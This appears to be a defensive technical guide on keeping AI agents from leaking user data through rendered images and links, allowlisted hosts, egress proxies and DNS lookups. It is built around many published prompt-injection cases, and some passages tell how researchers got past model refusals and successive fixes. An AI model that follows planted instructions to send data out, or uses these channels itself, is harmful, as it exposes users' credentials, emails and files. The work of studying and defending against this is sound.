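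Storing images in advance lets an application display them in an answer without requiring a click. When the agent opens a page, the application's server downloads every image on it and assigns each one an internal number. The model can refer to an image only by its number, and the user's browser loads the stored copy from the application. The server has to download all the images before the model chooses any. If it downloaded only the chosen ones, the attacker could infer the model's choices from the requests, as in CamoLeak. The safest time to download is before any private data has entered the context. If the context already contains private data when the agent opens a page, downloading every image reveals nothing beyond the choice of page, which another control has to limit.

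Links cause a subtler problem because people expect to click them. Markdown lets a model put any label on any address, and Legit Security got GitLab Duo to present a malicious address as safe. Showing the full address next to the label gives users a chance to notice an unfamiliar host or a long query string. This would have done little against SearchLeak, which started with a link to a real Microsoft site. Reddy and Gujral suggest stripping query parameters from allowed links, but this breaks many search and document links, and an attacker can put the data in the path instead.

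### Parsing to a strict subset

The filter in the EchoLeak case looked for text in a particular form, while the browser displayed whatever the Markdown parser recognised as a link or an image. An attacker needs only one way of writing a link or image that the parser recognises and the filter misses. Microsoft (2025) lists "deterministic blocking of known data exfiltration methods" among its defences against prompt injection. This is useful, but it doesn't stop an attacker who uses a syntax or relay that nobody has reported yet.

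Parsing avoids the mismatch. The application parses the answer once and builds the display only from the kinds of element it permits. On each streaming update it can work through these steps:

1. Join the new text to the text received so far and parse the whole with raw HTML switched off. The result is a tree of headings, paragraphs, lists, links and so on.
2. Copy only the permitted elements into a new tree. An element that is not on the list becomes plain text.
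3. For each link, read the address that the parser found, whichever style the model used. Require `https` and an exact match with an approved host, and otherwise show the address as text that the user can't click.
4. Replace each image with its description, or with a stored copy if the application has one.
5. Create the page elements from the new tree instead of inserting a string of HTML.

An unfinished image then appears as a few stray characters until the rest arrives. The same steps would have handled the reference style in EchoLeak and the raw HTML in GitLab Duo and SearchLeak, because the steps don't depend on how the model wrote the image. CamoLeak used ordinary images on an approved host, so only the rule for images in step 4 would have helped.

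A subset without HTML, diagrams or formulas makes some technical answers harder to read. Developers who add one of those features need to check what network requests its renderer makes. One of the coding agents that Lee and colleagues examined leaked an API key through a diagram renderer.

### An example policy

This policy suits a chat page that keeps its own images on a separate host, `images.example.com`. The browser receives the CSP as a single header, and the line breaks are only for readability.

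```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'self';
  style-src 'self';
  font-src 'self';
  img-src https://images.example.com;
  connect-src 'self';
  form-action 'none';
  base-uri 'none'
Referrer-Policy: no-referrer
```

| Directive | Effect |
|---|---|
| `default-src 'none'` | Refuses every type of resource that has no line of its own, such as video, embedded frames and plugins |
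| `script-src 'self'` | Runs only script files from the application's own host, and no scripts written into the page |
| `style-src 'self'` | Applies only style sheets from the application's own host, and no styles written into an answer |
| `font-src 'self'` | Refuses outside fonts, one of the routes that Microsoft 365 Copilot's preview pane left open |
| `img-src` | Loads pictures from one host, including background pictures that a style sheet requests |
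| `connect-src 'self'` | Limits the requests that the page's scripts send |
| `form-action 'none'` | Stops forms on the page from submitting anywhere; `default-src` doesn't cover this |
| `base-uri 'none'` | Prevents a tag in an answer from redirecting the page's relative addresses to another host; `default-src` doesn't cover this either |
| `Referrer-Policy` | A separate header that keeps the address of the chat page from reaching sites that the user opens from it |

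The `img-src` line needs the most care. `images.example.com` should only serve stored files. Allowing `'self'` instead would be riskier if the application's main host also offers link previews or an image proxy, since either could relay data to an outside server. Shared hosts are riskier still. Willison records leaks through a Google Forms address that Superhuman's email client allowed, and through an expired domain that was still on Salesforce's list of allowed domains.

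A rule that lists a path as well as a host allows fewer URLs. If Microsoft had approved only the Teams paths that serve pictures, the browser would have refused a direct request to the relay. But after a redirect, the browser ignores the path and checks only the scheme, host and port, as trackr.live's unsigned blog post *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* points out. An attacker could therefore get around the narrower rule with an open redirect, an address that forwards visitors to any other address included in its URL, if the redirect was on an approved path and the relay's host was also on the list.

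Reddy and Gujral recommend `script-src 'none'` for model output. A chat page needs its own scripts, so it can't run under that rule, but developers can apply it to a separate frame that holds only the answer. They then have to handle the frame's size, its scrolling and the copying of text themselves.

Enforcing a strict policy immediately will probably break something. Browsers also accept a `Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only` header, which reports violations without blocking them. trackr.live advises running it long enough to include rare jobs, such as quarterly reports, and then building the list of approved hosts from the results. The violation reports won't reveal a relay, because they cover only the browser's requests. In SearchLeak, Bing's server sent the request to the attacker. Finding relays requires checking what each approved host does with a URL it receives.

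## Deciding which domains an agent may reach

A domain allowlist names the hosts that an agent's browser, fetch tool or code sandbox may contact and blocks all others. It has the same weakness as the image policies behind EchoLeak and SearchLeak, because it approves a host by name, whatever that host does with a URL. The safety of the data also depends on who can read what the host receives, and for many well-known hosts that includes strangers.

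Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (2026) describes how the company's engineers changed their view of their allowlist after a leak. They had thought of it as a filter on destinations and now think of each entry as a "capability grant". Allowing a host allows every function it offers, including those the agent will never need.

Published cases show five ways an outsider can read a request sent to an allowed host. The host may record requests and show them to whoever set up the recording. It may give accounts to anyone, including the attacker. It may forward visitors to another site, or publish counts of what people download. Its domain registration may also have lapsed, letting the attacker buy the name.

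### What a list stops

An allowlist with gaps is still useful because it blocks every unlisted host, whatever the model tries to do. In a controlled exercise at Anthropic in February 2026, a researcher tricked a colleague into giving Claude Code, the company's coding agent, a prompt that mixed ordinary setup steps with an instruction to send the colleague's cloud credentials to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 repeats. Because the instruction came from the user, the model's defences had nothing unusual to detect. Anthropic concludes that only limits on the environment work in this situation, such as blocking the outgoing connection and keeping the credentials file out of reach.

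A list of allowed domains also saves the user from approving every connection. Anthropic runs Claude Code's network traffic through a proxy that allows listed domains and prompts the user about new ones. The proxy and limits on which files the agent can write form a sandbox, which cut permission prompts by 84 percent.

A short list of allowed hosts also makes attackers work harder. In *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click*, Luz (2026), a researcher at the firm Oasis Security, set out to get data from a plain Claude chat with no connected tools. Claude's code sandbox blocked requests to arbitrary servers, so he had to look for a weakness in the few hosts it allowed. He found one, but the defender could have checked the same hosts.

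A list of allowed domains restricts only the traffic that is checked against it. The Cloud Security Alliance's *Top 6 Claude Cowork Security Risks to Watch* warns that web search and web fetch in Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, bypass its egress controls. The documentation mentions this, but administrators can easily miss it.

### Services that record requests

`webhook.site` lets anyone create an address and watch the requests that arrive there. Developers use it to see exactly what a program sends, and an attacker can use it the same way to collect data that an agent puts in a URL.

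PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* (November 2025) describes a test of Google's code editor Antigravity. A developer asked its agent to follow an online integration guide that contained instructions in one-point type. The agent collected code and cloud credentials from the project. Antigravity's default settings blocked its file reader from opening the credentials file, so the agent printed the file with a terminal command. It then wrote a URL containing the credentials and had a subagent open it in a browser.

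Antigravity restricts the agent's browser to a list of approved sites. The list Google supplied included `webhook.site`, so the page opened and the attacker could read the credentials in the site's log. PromptArmor had accepted the recommended settings, which let the agent decide when to ask a person for review.

PromptArmor did not report the flaw privately because Google already warned new users about data exfiltration, and PromptArmor's report does not mention a fix. Removing `webhook.site` from the list of allowed domains would close this route, but PromptArmor found three others that did not use the browser tools.

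A form can also record requests, though a reviewer may not expect this of a document service. Google Forms uses the host `docs.google.com`. A form's owner can create a link with the answers already filled in, and opening a certain kind of link submits them. The email client Superhuman allowed images from that host in its CSP.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack in which a user asks Superhuman's assistant to summarise recent mail, including an unopened message that contains text planted by the attacker. The assistant answers with a Markdown image whose URL points to the attacker's Google Form and contains the contents of other emails. When the user's browser tries to load the image, its GET request submits the form, and Google stores the emails as a response. A single answer could leak several whole emails, or parts of more than 40.

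PromptArmor reported the vulnerability on Friday, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on December 8, shipped a first patch on December 9, and released more patches until January 11. Correcting the image list would not have been enough, because the assistant's web search could open any URL.

The same trick then worked in OpenAI's Codex, which began as a coding agent but had come to handle email too. According to PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data*, the firm reported the flaw on April 21, 2026, and OpenAI has fixed it. Anyone reviewing an allowlist should treat `docs.google.com` as a host that accepts messages from the public.

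### Hosts where anyone may hold an account

An agent often has to contact a service where its user has an account. If the attacker can also open an account there, the agent can send data to the attacker's account at the same host name.

Anthropic's API had this problem. In 2025, the company let Claude's code sandbox make network requests, with a default setting called "Package managers only". Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* reports that the first entry on the setting's short list of allowed domains was `api.anthropic.com`. That API includes a Files API, which customers use to upload files to their own accounts.

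Rehberger planted instructions and an API key for his own account in a document. When a user asked Claude to summarise it, Claude saved the user's last conversation to a file and uploaded the file with Rehberger's key. Claude refused many versions of the planted text before he found one that worked reliably. According to the documentation, each file could be up to 30 megabytes, thousands of times more than a URL can carry.

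He reported the flaw on October 25, 2025, and Anthropic closed the report an hour later as out of scope. Five days later, Anthropic said it should not have closed the report.

The route was still open when Anthropic released Cowork in January 2026. Two days after the release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed how an attacker could steal a loan estimate from a folder the user had connected. The planted text was in a document disguised as a skill file, and Cowork never asked for approval. The demonstration used Claude Haiku, a small model, but in a separate test the stronger Opus 4.5 also uploaded customer records to an attacker's account.

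Luz's attempt on the same API is the most useful for a reviewer because it shows that two functions on one host, reached with the same key, can differ in whether they let an attacker read the data. He first considered having Claude send the stolen text as a prompt, using the attacker's key. That would have failed because account holders cannot see the prompts that someone sends with their keys. Uploading the text through the Files API worked because an account holder can have a model read out an uploaded file.

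Anthropic fixed the Cowork leak with a proxy that rejects API keys other than the session's own. It is less clear whether the leak is fixed in ordinary Claude chats. Luz wrote in March 2026 that Anthropic was still addressing the issue, and Oasis Security's *Hijacking Claude Desktop Through the claude:// URL Scheme*, a later, undated report, describes the upload route as working on a default installation.

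### Links that forward to another site

If a check covers only the first host, an open redirect on that host can send the request to another host that was never checked.

Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* describes such a case in the check that ChatGPT ran before loading an image. The check always approved addresses on `bing.com`, and Bing wraps each search result in a `bing.com` link that forwards to the real site. The security firm got its own pages into Bing's index and used their wrapped links as image addresses, which ChatGPT loaded.

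If Bing forwards only links it has wrapped itself, the model cannot add private data to them. The attacker then has to prepare many pages and let the model choose among them, so each image can leak only a few bits, as in the attack on Claude with 27 links. Tenable reported the flaw on December 10, 2024, and was still asking for an update on March 4, 2025. The advisory lists no fix, but OpenAI's stronger check of August 2025 may have closed this route.

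Luz found an open redirect on `claude.com` and used it to reach victims. Google Ads requires an ad's displayed address and its actual link to have the same host. With the redirect, an ad could display `claude.com` and send people who clicked it to a Claude chat with hidden instructions already in the prompt box. If the user pressed Enter, data left through the Files API. Anthropic has fixed the hidden instructions and, according to Oasis Security's later report, dealt with this way of delivering them. The same redirect would have worked on an agent whose allowlist included `claude.com` and checked only the first address.

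A check that runs once, on the URL as the model wrote it, misses any host that the URL redirects to. An egress proxy checks again after a redirect, as a browser does under a CSP, because reaching the next host requires a new connection, which the proxy can refuse. Developers of fetch tools can either check every URL in the redirect chain against the allowlist or refuse redirects. Neither measure stops a relay like the Teams service in EchoLeak.

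### Public counters

An attacker can sometimes read data from a host without receiving requests or seeing logs. Claude Code's WebFetch tool opens web pages, and Anthropic had approved `huggingface.co` for it in advance. Anyone can publish AI models on Hugging Face, which counts how often their files are downloaded.

MITRE's *Claude Code* (2026), an entry in the public catalogue of software flaws (CVE-2026-54316), explains that approval of a bare host name covered every path on it. Text planted by an attacker could direct Claude Code to request files from the attacker's repositories. Claude Code made these requests without asking the user and ignored `--allowedTools`, an option that restricts what the agent may do. Each request raised a download count, and the attacker could read the stolen data from the pattern of counts.

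Leaking data through download counters is slow. A counter shows how many requests arrived but not their order, so an attacker who wants a six-digit code could need 60 counters, one for each possible digit in each position, and six downloads. Other people's downloads would add noise, although a new repository that nobody knows about would get few of them. A few hundred counters would be enough to leak a cryptographic key.

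Version 2.1.163 fixed the flaw, which affected versions from 0.2.54 onward. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) says that users with automatic updates had received the fix by June 17. It rates the flaw 6.5 out of 10, although the channel could carry files, environment variables and command output.

Expert Insights' *Researcher Finds Same Trust Flaw Across Claude Code, Gemini CLI, And Codex* reports that the researcher, Meged, first found a way to run commands. After Anthropic removed access to the shell, he took secrets out through read commands that needed no approval, a narrower channel. After a further fix, he used the download counters, which were narrower still.

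### Domains that lapse

An allowlist entry is a domain name, and the domain's owner can change. Salesforce's Agentforce lets companies build AI agents that work with their customer records. Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature turns submissions to a form on a company's public website into sales leads, so anyone who fills in the form can place text where an agent will read it.

The security firm Noma used this feature in an attack it named ForcedLeak. When an employee asked the agent about the new lead, the agent followed the planted text and put the email addresses of other leads into the URL of an image. A CSP should have blocked the image, but it still allowed every subdomain of `my-salesforce-cms.com`, whose registration had expired. The domain was on sale for $5, according to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*. Willison recounts that the researchers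 registered it and found the lead data in their server's logs.

ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* dates the vulnerability report to July 28, 2025. On September 8, Salesforce began enforcing "Trusted URLs", which keeps its agents from producing links to unapproved domains. Noma published its findings on September 25. Salesforce also corrected its Content Security Policy (CSP) and, as Noma told Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, regained control of the domain.

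Reviewing the CSP when Salesforce added the entry would not have revealed a problem. The entry became dangerous later, when the domain's registration expired, without anyone editing the list.

### Reviewing one entry

A reviewer can work through a candidate host in seven steps.

1. Write down what the agent needs from the host, including the paths and methods. If nobody can name a task that needs it, leave it out. Anthropic gives similar advice in its deployment documentation, because an agent can send data to any domain that the proxy allows.
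2. Open an account as a stranger would. From inside the agent's sandbox, use that account's credentials to write something to the host, then try to read it from outside.
3. Look for anything that shows activity to other people, such as form responses, download counts or visitor statistics.
4. Find every feature that accepts a URL and give it the address of a test server. If the agent's own client arrives at the test server, the host has a redirect. If the request comes from the host's network, the host is a relay.
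5. Replace wildcards with the subdomains that the agent actually uses.
6. Look up who owns the domain and when its registration expires.
7. Record the reason for the entry, the person responsible and a date for the next review.

The issue in step 5 dates back to at least 2023, when Google's Bard assistant loaded images from any host under `google.com`. Willison explains in *Hacking Google Bard* that these hosts included `script.google.com`, where anyone can run a small program that receives requests. Google said it had fixed the flaw.

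The next review date matters even for a domain that isn't at risk of lapsing, because services add features. Luz notes that the Files API was still in beta when he used it. An entry for `api.anthropic.com` approved before that API existed would have started allowing file uploads without any change to the list.

### A package registry and a code host

Coding agents need to install packages and copy source code, so package registries and code hosts are among the first entries on most allowlists. The npm registry, which distributes JavaScript packages, and GitHub both do badly in the review.

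| Question | `registry.npmjs.org` | `github.com` |
|---|---|---|
| Can a stranger hold an account? | Yes | Yes |
| Can the agent write to a stranger's account? | Yes, by publishing a package with the stranger's token | Yes, by pushing code with the stranger's token |
| Does the host show activity to outsiders? | Yes, it publishes download counts for each package | Yes, a repository's owner can see how many people visited or cloned it |
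| Does the host contact other addresses? | Not when it serves a package | Yes, it can notify an outside address of each change to a repository |
| Is the domain likely to lapse? | No | No |

An npm package can also name a dependency at any web address. The sandbox itself requests that dependency, so the allowlist blocks the request if the host isn't listed.

The agent only needs to download packages from the npm registry. A proxy that decrypts traffic can allow only GET requests, which stops the agent from publishing packages. This also breaks npm's security audit, which sends the project's list of dependencies by POST. Data can still leak through download counts, because an attacker can publish many packages and see which ones the agent installs.

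An internal mirror, a server that keeps copies of packages, can also stop an agent from leaking data through npm's public download counts, but only if the company stocks it in advance. If the mirror fetches missing packages from npm on request, the agent can still raise those counts. Stocking it in advance means someone has to approve each new package before the agent can use it.

GitHub is harder, because a rule that allows only GET breaks copying. When Git copies a repository over HTTPS, it sends a POST request to a path that ends in `git-upload-pack`. When it pushes code, the path ends in `git-receive-pack`. The names describe what the server does, not the agent. A proxy can allow the first path and refuse the second, and can limit both to the company's own repositories. If the agent needs public code from elsewhere, each outside repository needs its own entry. Allowing all of them would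 let the agent reach the attacker's repositories again, and their visitor counts can leak data.

The same company may also list `api.github.com`, the host through which programs use GitHub. That host needs its own review, since a program can create issues, comments and repositories there without Git.

### Paths and tenants

An allowlist entry can include a path, which limits the agent to part of a host. If Anthropic had approved only the documentation at `huggingface.co/docs/`, Claude Code would have asked the user before opening an attacker's repository. The rule has to run in a component that can read the path, such as a fetch tool or a proxy that decrypts traffic.

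Small mistakes in matching can undo a path rule. An entry for `/acme` without a trailing slash also matches `/acme-files`, which a stranger may own. The path `/acme/../other` begins with the approved text, but the server resolves it to `/other`. The checking code should therefore reduce the address to its final form before comparing it, then send that form instead of the original.

Some shared services give each customer, or tenant, its own subdomain. A company can then allow only its own, such as `acme.sharepoint.com`. The allowlist exploited in EchoLeak instead used a wildcard that admitted every customer's site. Where all tenants use one host, as on Anthropic's API, the host name doesn't identify the account that receives the data. Rehberger proposed that the sandbox let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

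Even a company's own tenant may have public parts, such as a support forum or an open repository. An agent with the user's credentials can copy private data there, where an attacker can read it. Anthropic lists credentials for allowed domains among the limitations of its sandbox for this kind of reason. The reviewer should therefore check what the agent can write as well as where it can write.

### The size of default lists

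Most users start with the vendor's allowlist. In June 2025, OpenAI's Codex offered a ready-made list of 71 common domains. Suppose that careful review misses a leak in one entry out of a hundred. A list of 71 entries has about a 51 percent chance of containing at least one leak, and a list of seven has about a 7 percent chance. The odds depend much more on which hosts are listed than on the length of the list, because code hosts and form services can leak data through their normal functions.

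Short lists can contain such hosts too. Pluto Security's *Inside Claude Managed Agents* decoded the access token from one session of Anthropic's hosted agent service in April 2026 and found seven allowed hosts. They included `api.github.com`, `api.anthropic.com`, `sentry.io`, which collects error reports for software companies, and `statsig.com`, which collects usage data. All four give accounts to the public. A proxy may restrict what each accepts, so the list alone doesn't prove a leak, but a reviewer would want to run step 2 on every one.

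A default's label can also mislead. Someone who chose "Package managers only" had no reason to expect access to an API for uploading files, and Rehberger warned that other hosts on that list might allow similar attacks. Starting with an empty list is safer. The administrator can then review the hosts in the proxy's log of refused connections and add those that pass, though some tasks will fail in the first weeks. Teams that keep the vendor's list can at least save a copy and compare it after each update, since a new version may add hosts without the administrator's approval.

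## Enforcing the domain list with a proxy

An allowlist works only if a program checks every outgoing connection against it. For sandboxed agents, that program is usually an egress proxy, which runs outside the sandbox so that the model's commands can't change it. How much the proxy stops depends on whether traffic can go around it, which program looks up host names, and whether the proxy can read the requests it forwards.

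### One request, step by step

Suppose an agent in a sandbox runs a command that fetches `https://files.example.com/reports/2026?user=ana`.

1. The command finds the proxy's address in an environment variable such as `HTTPS_PROXY`. It doesn't look up `files.example.com` itself.
2. It connects to the proxy and sends `CONNECT files.example.com:443`, a readable request to open a tunnel to that host.
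3. The proxy compares the name with its list and answers with an error if the name isn't there.
4. If the name passes, the proxy looks up the host's address, connects to it, and from then on copies bytes in both directions.
5. The command sets up encryption with the server through the tunnel. It gives the host name again, usually still readable, so that the server can choose the right certificate.
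6. Inside the encryption, the command sends the method, path and query string, and names the host once more in a header.

The proxy decides in step 3. The private value passes in step 6, when the proxy sees only encrypted bytes.

A program can sometimes reach a blocked site through an allowed one, using a technique called domain fronting. It relies on content delivery networks, which serve many unrelated sites from the same machines. The program asks the proxy for an allowed site on such a network but puts a different site's name in the encrypted host header, and some networks then pass the request to the other site. Anthropic lists domain fronting as a limitation of Claude Code's proxy, which relies on the name the client supplies. Docker, whose agent sandboxes also filter by domain, calls it inherent to HTTPS proxying, although a proxy that decrypts traffic can check that the header matches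 the approved name.

Claude Code's proxy has had two bugs in the comparison in step 3. Before version 2.0.55, an empty allowlist let commands reach every host, although it was documented as blocking all network access (CVE-2025-66479). Daily Security Review's *Anthropic Silently Fixed Claude Code Null-Byte Sandbox Escape* reports that a host name containing a null byte could bypass the allowlist from October 20, 2025 to March 31, 2026. Some software treats a null byte as the end of a text and some doesn't, so two parts of a program can read different names from the same bytes. Anthropic fixed the null-byte bug in version 2.1.88 without a security notice or a CVE number, so a company that updates only in response to advisories would have had no reason to install that version.

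### Letting the proxy read the traffic

*Codex CLI MITM Hooks* (Vaughan, 2026) describes how the proxy in OpenAI's Codex decrypts requests. When the agent asks for a tunnel to `api.github.com`, the proxy has its own certificate authority sign a new certificate for that name and presents it to the agent. The agent's encryption then ends at the proxy, which can read the request and apply rules to its method, path, query string and headers before sending it on over a second encrypted connection.

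The client accepts that certificate only if it trusts the proxy's certificate authority, so someone has to install the authority's certificate in the sandbox. Some language runtimes keep their own list of authorities, and the certificate has to be added there too. Anthropic warns that `gh`, `gcloud` and `terraform` may reject certificates inside its macOS sandbox. It suggests either using the `enableWeakerNetworkIsolation` setting, for people who run a decrypting proxy, or running the tool outside the sandbox with the user's full access. Outside the sandbox, the proxy no longer restricts `gh`, which can write to any GitHub repository its user can.

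Clients that use certificate pinning accept only a certificate or key they already know, so they reject the certificates the proxy generates. The operator can either stop using such a client or exempt the host it connects to from decryption, in which case the proxy can check only the host name.

A decrypting proxy also holds every password, token and document that passes through it, and its logs may keep them. Anyone who steals the certificate authority's private key can impersonate any website to a machine that trusts that authority. It is safer to trust the authority only inside the sandbox and to keep its key outside.

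Claude Code has an experimental setting, `network.tlsTerminate`, that makes its proxy decrypt traffic so that it can fill in credentials, but Anthropic states that this adds no content filtering. An operator who wants to filter paths or content has to supply their own proxy. That proxy has to do all the filtering, because Claude Code's allowed and denied domains, approval prompts and check for local addresses no longer apply to traffic sent to it.

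### Settings that close particular routes

A program can ignore the environment variable in step 1, so the sandbox must have no route out except the proxy. On Linux, Claude Code runs each sandboxed command in a network namespace (a separate set of network connections) that isn't connected to the user's network. On macOS, the operating system by default blocks every connection except the one to the proxy. UDP, the protocol most DNS lookups use instead of TCP, can't leave the sandbox at all. Most database drivers and plain `ssh` don't use the proxy, so they fail even for allowed hosts.

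An allowed name can also resolve to a private address, such as `169.254.169.254`, where many cloud machines can request their own credentials. Claude Code's proxy has refused such local addresses since version 2.1.284, but it still connects to an intranet host in a private range if the host is on the list. Codex blocks private ranges, but OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes the check as best-effort, because an attacker who controls a domain's DNS can give one address for the check and another for the connection. To prevent this completely, the proxy would have to connect to the exact address it checked.

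#### Redirects

A redirect to another host needs a new tunnel, so the proxy checks the list again. The data in the first URL has already reached the allowed host, but the proxy keeps it from reaching the attacker's host.

A redirect to another path on the same host goes through the tunnel that is already open, so a proxy with path rules has to check every request, not just every connection. Fetch tools outside the sandbox follow their own rules. For example, Claude Code's sandbox allowlist doesn't apply to its WebFetch tool. A reviewer can set up a redirect from an allowed test host to an unlisted one, then request the redirecting URL with every tool that fetches pages. The unlisted host's web log should stay empty.

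#### Methods and paths

OpenAI's *Agent internet access* describes a setting for Codex's cloud version that allows only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests. In OpenAI's example of a leak, a bug report tells the agent to run a command that sends the latest commit message to an outside site by POST. The setting would block that command but not a GET request with the same message in the query string, because all three permitted methods send the full URL. Headers can carry data as well. The HTTP format also does not prevent a GET request from having a body, so the proxy should refuse those bodies.

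The setting still reduces how much data each request can carry. Rehberger's upload to Anthropic's API could move 30 megabytes at once. A URL of 8,000 characters holds about 6,000 bytes of encoded data, so sending the same file through URLs would take about 5,000 requests. That is slow enough for someone counting requests to notice, but a password fits in a single request.

A proxy can enforce HTTP method rules on HTTPS traffic only if it decrypts the traffic. Otherwise, it has to refuse every HTTPS connection or allow every method.

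Path rules also need decryption. The firewall for GitHub Copilot's cloud agent, which works on code in GitHub's own environment, allows rules that name a URL such as `https://packages.contoso.corp/project-1/`. The agent can then reach that path and anything beneath it, but not `/project-2`.

The same host entry can mean different things in different products. In Copilot's firewall, `packages.contoso.corp` also covers every subdomain. In Codex's local proxy, the same entry covers only that host, while the prefix `*.` covers only subdomains and `**.` covers both. A list copied from Codex to Copilot therefore allows more hosts than its author intended. OpenAI's ready-made list for cloud tasks includes `google.com` and `azure.com`. If those entries cover subdomains, the agent can reach Google Forms and virtual machines that anyone can rent, so it is worth testing whether they do before choosing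 the list.

#### Credentials

Allowing a host where anyone can hold an account lets an agent upload data with the attacker's key. A decrypting proxy can prevent this by removing any credential from the outgoing request and attaching the one that belongs to the current user's session. The sandbox never holds a real key. If injected text supplies the attacker's key, the proxy discards it and the file ends up in the user's own account. The proxy can instead refuse the request, as Anthropic's fix for Cowork does, which also leaves a record of the attempt.

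Claude Code's credential masking is similar, but it protects the user's key without ensuring that requests use the user's account. Sandboxed commands see a placeholder, which the proxy replaces with the real value on requests to approved hosts. Anthropic's documentation doesn't describe any check for other keys in a request. It notes that masking doesn't affect requests to Amazon's cloud signed with unmasked credentials, so an attacker's own Amazon keys would still work if the storage host is on the allowlist.

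Masking also needs a list, `injectHosts`, of the hosts that may receive the credential's real value. If the list is missing, the proxy supplies that value to every allowed domain. Tests of credential binding should also cover keys sent in the query string, in a cookie and in the request body, since many services accept keys in more than one place.

### Leaks through name lookups

A sandbox that blocks every web connection can still leak data in the domain names its programs look up. Researchers have disclosed this flaw in a coding agent and, in 2026, in two hosted code sandboxes.

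Claude Code asked developers to approve shell commands but exempted some it treated as harmless. Rehberger found that the exempt commands included `ping`, `nslookup`, `host` and `dig`, which all look up domain names. In his test, text in a source file led Claude to read an API key from the project's configuration and put it in a subdomain of his site. Claude refused to contact domains known for security testing but accepted an ordinary one, so the refusal would not have stopped a real attacker.

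He reported the flaw, CVE-2025-55284, on May 26, 2025, and suggested removing the four commands from the exempt list. Anthropic reported it fixed on June 6, in version 1.0.4. *CVE-2025-55284 Detail*, the entry in the US government's National Vulnerability Database, attributes the flaw to an overly broad allowlist of safe commands. Correcting that list closes the reported route, but an approved test suite or build script can also look up domain names, and the sandbox that would stop those lookups is still off by default.

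ChatGPT runs code for its users in a Linux environment that was supposed to have no internet access. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a path out of this environment that could carry a user's messages and uploaded files after a single malicious prompt. A custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that someone else has configured, could also have used this path. The Hacker News (2026) identifies the path as DNS requests and reports that OpenAI fixed the problem on February 20, 2026, and that there was no evidence of malicious use.

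Amazon Web Services (AWS) sells a similar environment, the AgentCore Code Interpreter, to companies that build agents. According to Unit 42, the research team of the security firm Palo Alto Networks, AWS originally described the interpreter's sandbox mode as "complete isolation with no external access." Unit 42 and a second firm, BeyondTrust, found that the isolation was incomplete. BeyondTrust's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter’s ‘Sandbox’ mode allows DNS queries* (2026) reports that the mode allowed DNS lookups, which the researchers used to send data out and to control the sandbox interactively, since a name server's answers can carry commands back.

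AWS first changed its description. VPNCentral's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore sandbox bypass allows covert DNS C2 and data exfiltration* quotes the new wording as "limited external network access", with access to Amazon's S3 storage and DNS. BeyondTrust updated its account on April 22, 2026 to say that AWS had since taken further steps and that data could no longer leave through DNS.

The remedy is to give the sandbox no working resolver and have the proxy do all lookups, checking the list before resolving each name, as in the steps above. If the proxy resolves a name first, any data in the name leaks even if the proxy then refuses the connection. Claude Code's proxy resolves a name only after it passes the allowlist. You can test another product by requesting an unlisted subdomain of a test domain and reading the log of that domain's name server. Any lookup in the log is a leak, even if the agent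 received an error.

### Attacks and the settings that stop them

Each column shows the effect of one setting alone. "Path rule" means that the setting helps only if the attacker needs a path that isn't approved.

| Attack | Host list, no direct route | Lookups only by the proxy | Decryption with path and method rules | Only the session's credential |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Query string to an unlisted host | Stops it | No | No | No |
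| Data in a DNS lookup | No | Stops it | No | No |
| Redirect to an unlisted host | Stops it | No | No | No |
| Domain fronting | No | No | Stops it if the proxy compares host names | No |
| Upload to a stranger's account on a listed host | No | No | Stops uploads by POST or PUT | Stops it |
| Query string to a listed host that records requests | No | No | Path rule | No |
| Relay on a listed host | No | No | Path rule | No |
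| Download counts on a listed host | No | No | Path rule | No |
| Request from a component outside the proxy | No | No | No | No |

### What the vendors' sandboxes enforce

| Product | Network access by default | What a rule can name | What the rules don't cover |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | Unrestricted by the sandbox, which is off; once on, each new host needs approval | Host, subdomains, port | Web tools, local tool servers, hooks |
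| Codex on a user's machine | None for commands | Host, subdomains | Connectors, tool servers, browser |
| Codex cloud | None once setup is finished | Host, method | Setup scripts |
| Copilot cloud agent | GitHub's own hosts and a recommended list | Host with its subdomains, or a URL path | Tool servers, setup steps |
| AWS AgentCore, sandbox mode | Amazon S3 | A network mode for the whole interpreter | Whatever S3 itself allows |

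When a command fails in the sandbox, Claude Code may retry it outside. In manual mode the user normally gets a prompt, but a rule that approves `curl`, for example, also approves the retry. Setting `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to false prevents these retries. Administrators also need `failIfUnavailable`, because Claude Code otherwise runs commands without a sandbox when the sandbox can't start. With `strictAllowlist`, the proxy blocks unlisted hosts instead of prompting the user.

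Codex on a user's machine has stricter defaults, but one line of configuration can undo them. If a user turns on network access for commands without also turning on the proxy, the commands get unrestricted direct access. The newer permission profiles, described in OpenAI's *Permissions*, also give full access when the network is on and there are no domain rules. OpenAI adds that domain rules don't determine whether an allowed destination is trustworthy.

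Codex cloud runs setup scripts before the agent starts, with full internet access and the secrets they need to install software. OpenAI then removes the secrets and, unless the user has changed the default, cuts off the network. An attacker who hijacks the agent with malicious text therefore can't get those secrets or, by default, use the network, but a malicious package installed during setup would have had access to both.

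GitHub's firewall covers only processes that the agent starts through its shell tool, and GitHub warns that sophisticated attacks may bypass it. Since April 2026, administrators have been able to configure the firewall for a whole organisation (GitHub, *Organization firewall settings for Copilot cloud agent*, 2026). By default, each repository still has its own settings, and its administrators can add hosts. When the firewall blocks a request, Copilot posts the blocked address and the command in the pull request. This alerts reviewers to an attack, but in a public repository it could also publish any private data in the address, unless GitHub removes the data first.

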